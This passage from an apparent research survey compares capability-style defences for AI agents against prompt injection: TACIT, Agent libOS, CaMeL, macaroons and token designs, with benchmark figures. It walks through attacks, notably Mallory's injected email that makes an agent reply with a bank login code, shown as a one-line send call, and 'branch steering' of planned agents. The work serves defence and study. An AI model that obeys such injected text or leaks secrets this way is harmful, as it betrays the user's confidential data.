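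Ordinary Scala code can get around this, for example by opening files by name through the standard library, or by using *reflection*, which lets a program find and call code that nobody gave it. TACIT therefore compiles the agent's code in a "safe mode" that forbids these features.

Older capability languages such as E also prevent a program from using a reference it doesn't have. Odersky and colleagues add *tracking*, which means that the type of each value lists the references the value could use. This helps with secrets. TACIT puts secret text in a wrapper called `Classified`, and a program can work on the contents only through a function that uses no references at all:

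```
secret.map(text => text.length)          # accepted: uses no references
secret.map(text => report.write(text))   # rejected: uses "report"
```

The program properly holds `report`, so an ordinary object-capability language would run the second line. TACIT's compiler rejects that line because the function's type includes `report`. The result of an accepted function stays wrapped. If the program prints it, the user sees the contents, but the agent's model receives only "Classified(\*\*\*\*)". A separate trusted model with no tools can summarise wrapped text, and the summary is wrapped too.

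Tracking also makes it easy to limit how long a program can use a reference. TACIT can give a program a reference to a folder for one block of code, and the compiler rejects any program that would keep the reference after the block ends, for example by returning a function that uses it.

TACIT's general-purpose library is less strict than this suggests. The agent's code requests a folder by writing its path, and requests network access by writing host names. Inside the folder, it opens files by path. The operator has to set any limits on which folders and hosts the agent may request, and can do so by editing the library. Another example from Odersky and colleagues is much closer to the object-capability model, because a person writes the environment in advance, and it contains one document database and one output file.

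Researchers have machine-checked proofs that the underlying type system is sound, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode needs a further proof. Programmers can also mark library code as safe, and the compiler accepts the label without checking the code. The guarantee doesn't cover outside programs that the agent starts or information leaked through timing.

To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues put API keys and confidential documents in a sample software project. They ran 120 trials per model with injected instructions and 11 in which the user asked for the secrets. Neither model leaked anything with the wrapper, which is unsurprising because the agent's model never received the secret text. Without the wrapper, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 of the 131 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11, mostly to malicious users. The more informative result is that the wrapper didn't reduce utility.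 Sonnet completed 99.2 percent of its tasks with the wrapper and 83.3 percent without it, and MiniMax completed 90.0 and 88.3 percent. Sonnet's lower score without the wrapper may have come from time limits and from stopping to warn the user about injections.

Writing Scala did little harm to the agents' performance. Three models did 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points better on customer-service tasks when they wrote programs instead of making tool calls. On a set of real software bugs, MiniMax fixed 41.7 percent with TACIT and 43.3 percent with ordinary tools. But the customer-service tools returned plain, unwrapped data, so those tests measured the effect of writing Scala but not the effect of keeping data secret. Compiling a typical program took less than a second. *What's in the Box* (2025) found that tracking took under 15 percent of the compiler's time on Scala's standard library.

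The types can list the references a function may use, but they can't yet exclude a whole kind of reference, such as those that give network access. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proposes extending the type system to allow this.

### Agent libOS

*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) keeps the references in a runtime that works like a small operating system for agents. The runtime is designed for agents that change after deployment, for example by loading new instructions, writing their own tools or starting other agents. Under Zhang's rule, a change in what an agent can see must not by itself give the agent authority over anything that already exists.

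The runtime keeps a full table of callable tools and a shorter list that it shows the model. Trusted workflows can still call the hidden tools, so hiding them provides no security in this design. The security check is in the function that directly accesses the file, repository or server.

A capability in Agent libOS is a record that names a resource, the permitted actions and the agent that holds it. It can also have an expiry date and a limit on uses. An action is allowed only if a capability covers it, it falls within the current task's limits and budget, and it either satisfies a fixed policy or gets a person's approval. A person's approval therefore can't make up for a missing capability.

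The model never handles these records, so it can't forge or leak them. But the model still writes a path or an identifier, and the runtime then looks for a record that covers the request. So Agent libOS, like CapScope, is closer to capabilities as rows than to object capabilities.

The check has to account for what an action does. For example, a model that can pass any arguments to Git, the version-control program, can make it run other code or send data to a new address. Agent libOS instead offers specific operations on one repository and the remote copies already configured for it.

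Zhang didn't prove these properties formally. In 33 scripted tasks, 119 actions ran, none of them unauthorized, and the runtime blocked no permitted actions. With a simple tool wrapper instead of the runtime, 20 of 29 actions were unauthorized, but Zhang deliberately made that baseline weak. With a real model, all 12 runs of four longer workflows were safe and successful. This is a small sample, and Zhang didn't test the system on AgentDojo, so we don't know how much it would reduce utility on that benchmark.

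He also measured the effect of hiding tools without changing the agents' authority. In 15 pairs of runs, agents saw either every tool or a short list they could expand. All 30 runs reached the right result. The short list cut the average input from about 104,000 tokens to 71,000, but raised the average number of model calls from 3.7 to 6.6.

### CaMeL: a plan written before the data arrives

The best-known prototype is CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* in March 2025. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) wrote that he had seen "alarmingly little progress" on prompt injection in two and a half years and that CaMeL was an exception.

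CaMeL builds on Willison's earlier idea of using two models. A *privileged* model reads the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. It never sees the emails or documents the plan will handle. In an example from TechSpot, the plan fetches an email with `email = get_last_email()`. A *quarantined* model reads the email and extracts whatever the plan needs, but has no tools. An interpreter runs the plan, calls the tools and stores the results in variables.

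An injected instruction therefore can't add a step to the plan, but it can still corrupt a value the plan uses, such as the address a document is sent to. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that CaMeL deals with this by tagging every value with its sources and the people who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy checks the tool, the arguments and their tags, then allows or denies the call. CaMeL calls these tags "capabilities", but they aren't capabilities in the sense used here, because a tag describes a piece of data and doesn't give access to anything.

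Odersky and colleagues ran TACIT on AgentDojo with the two models from CaMeL's evaluation and compared the results with CaMeL's published ones. The table gives the share of user tasks completed, apparently during attacks.

| Environment | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini | TACIT, o4-mini |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
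| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

Each system let through one attack with o4-mini and none with Gemini, out of 963 for each model. TACIT's failure was an answer that quoted hotel reviews containing the attacker's recommendation. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' utility comparable. That seems generous for o4-mini, since TACIT's completion rate was 21 points lower on Slack tasks and 28.5 points lower on Workspace tasks.

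TACIT probably stopped these attacks for much the same reason as CaMeL. It wrapped emails, files, web pages and reviews so that the model writing the programs didn't read them. The rule against using references on wrapped data may have contributed less. According to the model's instructions for this test, side effects inside functions applied to wrapped data run immediately, which suggests that the rule didn't cover actions like payments.

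*SecureClaw* (2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo with adapted code and found a greater loss of utility than these figures suggest. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. The paper's own system, which keeps the usual loop of calling a tool and reading the result, completed 59 but let a few attacks through.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) presents an agent called Randori and compares it with CaMeL. With its data policies on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 tasks with each of two models. With them off, it did about as well as Randori, which completed roughly twice as many. So in that test, the policies reduced the number of completed tasks far more than the separate planner did. TypeGuard, a similar system written in Haskell, completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without its policies and 8 with them, compared with 7 for CaMeL.

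The separate planner has drawbacks of its own. The privileged model must write code to handle a tool's output before seeing any, so developers must document the exact format of every result. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to teams of agents, reports that this documentation was necessary for reasonable utility on both of its benchmarks. The planner also works less well when the next step depends on what the agent finds. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applies the design to agents that operate a computer's screen, where this happens constantly. The planner writes one plan in advance, with branches for what might appear. Large commercial models kept at most 57 percent of their usual performance.

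Branches also give attackers a new way to influence the agent. If a plan does one thing when the quarantined model answers "yes" and another when it answers "no", an attacker can use a malicious page to influence the answer and so choose what the plan does. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* calls this "branch steering" and reports that it remained partly possible even with extra defences. Rajani and colleagues' true-or-false example has the same structure.

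### Signed tokens as keys

TACIT and CaMeL keep references inside one interpreter. A company whose agents call services on many computers can't do that, so it usually gives the agents tokens. This is the keys model, in which the holder presents a key along with the name of the resource it is requesting.

According to Cloudflare, an agent usually gets such a token by sending its user to an authorization page. Once the user approves, the service issues a token that the agent can use to act for the user. MCP uses the same process. "The agent" here should mean the software around the model.

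A *macaroon* is a token that its holder can weaken but not strengthen. The service computes a code from the token's identifier and a secret key. To add a restriction such as "read-only", the holder computes a new code from the restriction and the old code, and passes on only the new one. Removing the restriction would require the old code, which nobody can work out from the new one. An agent can therefore give a helper a weaker token without contacting the service. But a macaroon is a bearer token, so anyone who copies it can use it.

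Tallam (2026), in *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents*, applies the same idea to chains of agents. The last agent may do only what everyone in the chain may do:

effective permissions = C₁ ∩ C₂ ∩ … ∩ Cₙ

In Tallam's prototype, a helper agent can take an action only if the user, the planning agent and the helper are all allowed to take it. For example, if the user may read, send and delete mail, the planning agent may read and send, and the helper may read and delete, the helper can only read. This rule held in every trial, and each decision took a few millionths of a second. Tallam argues for the design's security properties but doesn't formally prove them, and hasn't tested the design with agents on a live benchmark, so its effect on utility is unknown.

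*Governing Dynamic Capabilities* (Zhou, 2026) gives each agent a signed certificate containing a hash (a short fingerprint) of its complete list of tools. When the agent requests a credential, a verifier hashes its current tools and refuses the request if the two hashes differ. An agent that gains a web browser therefore loses its access until somebody approves a new certificate. The check takes 97 millionths of a second. In tests with 5 to 20 agents, this check and the paper's other checks together caught all seven kinds of attack without false alarms and added less than 0.02 percent overhead. For closed-source tools, though, the hash covers only the public description, so the check would miss a change to the underlying code.

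These designs differ in what an attacker gains by getting a model to repeat everything in its prompt.

| Reference | Who holds it | Does it enter the prompt? | What can someone do with a copy of the text? |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Secret token given to the model | The model's context | Yes | Everything the token allows |
| Macaroon | The harness | It needn't | Everything the token allows |
| AgentCap token | Software outside the model | It needn't | Nothing, if they are a different agent |
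| Zhou's certificate | The agent's software | It needn't | Nothing, if the verifier also demands proof of the agent's private key |
| Agent libOS record | The runtime | No, only names do | Nothing without an agent that holds the record |
| TACIT reference | The Scala interpreter | No, only the variable's name does | Nothing outside that program's session |

A harness that keeps tokens out of the prompt recreates ambient authority if it attaches the right token to whatever call the model writes. An attacker who can steer the model then doesn't need to steal the token. The harness can avoid this only by choosing the token on some basis other than the model's call, such as the agent's current step in the task.

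### An agent that may both read and send

References restrict what an agent can reach, but it can still do harm with the ones it needs. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (Acharya and Gupta, 2026) gives the example of a tool that reads files and a tool that sends email. Neither is malicious, but together they can leak a file.

Email alone is enough for this attack. Ana asks her agent to answer her unread messages. One is from her bank and contains a login code. Another is from Mallory, an attacker, and asks the agent to include the code that the bank just sent. The harness has made the references as narrow as it can. For each message, the agent gets one reference that reads it and another that can reply only to its sender. The agent obeys Mallory and runs:

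```
reply_to_mallory.send(bank_message.read())
```

The narrow references would have stopped the attack if Mallory had asked the agent to forward the code to a third person, because the agent has no reference for writing to anyone else. But this line uses two references that the task requires and does only what they permit. A sandbox would also allow the line, since it permits both reading the mailbox and contacting the mail server.

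Whether this agent is a confused deputy depends on the definition. In Karp's definition, a deputy uses its permissions on something that another party designated. Mallory designated the bank's message, but in words, and the agent supplied the reference. The NCSC article by David C more broadly calls a system a confused deputy if someone can "coerce" it into doing something that benefits an attacker. Ana's agent clearly fits this broader definition. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks*, David C thinks developers can reduce this risk but not eliminate it, and that a language model may be the wrong choice for a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk.

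**Splitting the agent.** Ana's harness could start a separate agent for each message, with references to that message and its reply only. The agent that reads Mallory's message then can't reach the bank's, and the reachability argument guarantees this whatever Mallory writes, as long as the agents can't communicate. CaMeL can get the same result with a plan written in advance:

```
for message in unread_messages():
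    draft = quarantined_model("Write a reply", message)
    reply(message, draft)
```

The quarantined model sees one message at a time. Mallory can spoil the reply to Mallory but can't get the code into it.

Splitting works here because each reply needs only one message. If Sam wrote "Can you make the time Priya suggested?", the agent answering Sam would need Priya's message too. The agents could be allowed to ask each other questions, but then the agent answering Mallory could ask for the code. Splitting therefore suits tasks with a predictable structure. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) discusses a paper on such designs in which this limit is deliberate. The paper's patterns constrain agents "to explicitly prevent them from solving arbitrary tasks".

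The harness could instead let the agent read everything, track where the data came from, and check what goes into each reply. CaMeL's tags list Ana and the bank as the only permitted readers of the login code, so the policy blocks any text to Mallory that depends on the code.

It is hard to decide what depends on the code. If the quarantined model reads all the unread messages before it drafts a reply to Sam, the draft may contain something from any of them. A cautious system therefore has to give the draft the tags of every message. Sam isn't allowed to read the bank's message, so the system can't send Sam even a harmless "yes". Agent libOS takes this approach and never drops a label just because the model seems to have ignored part of its input. Tallam describes a blunter rule, under which an agent that has read something confidential can't send anything outside the company for the rest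 of the session.

TACIT's strict form avoids the question because it never sends wrapped data. Ana could read a draft on her own screen, but she would have to send it herself.

*The LLMbda Calculus* reports that many benchmark tasks need data flows that, in the words of TypeGuard's developers, "no secure policy would admit". Randori lets the developer endorse particular uses of untrusted data, much as Rajani and colleagues did for Hardy's compiler. Randori failed some tasks when endorsement was turned off, and turning it back on recovered them with a small, measured reduction in security.

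**Binding each permission to a purpose.** Agent libOS lets a developer set limits for a task that apply even if the agent has broader capabilities. If Ana asks only for a summary of her mail, the limits can rule out sending, so Mallory's attack fails even though the agent still has a general capability to send. PORTICO and AgentCap similarly tie permissions to a step or a stated purpose.

This doesn't help when Ana asks for replies, because "answer the unread messages" covers both the honest replies and the leak. The purpose would have to be as narrow as "answer Mallory using only Mallory's message", and enforcing that would require either splitting the agent or tracking the data.

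For sensitive data, Agent libOS can ask a person to approve one exact transfer. The approval works once and covers only a specific text, recipient and versions of the source data, so it no longer applies if the agent changes the text. Ana would see a message to Mallory with her login code in it and could refuse, but only if she notices the code. Odersky and colleagues point out that people who get many such requests tend to stop reading them.
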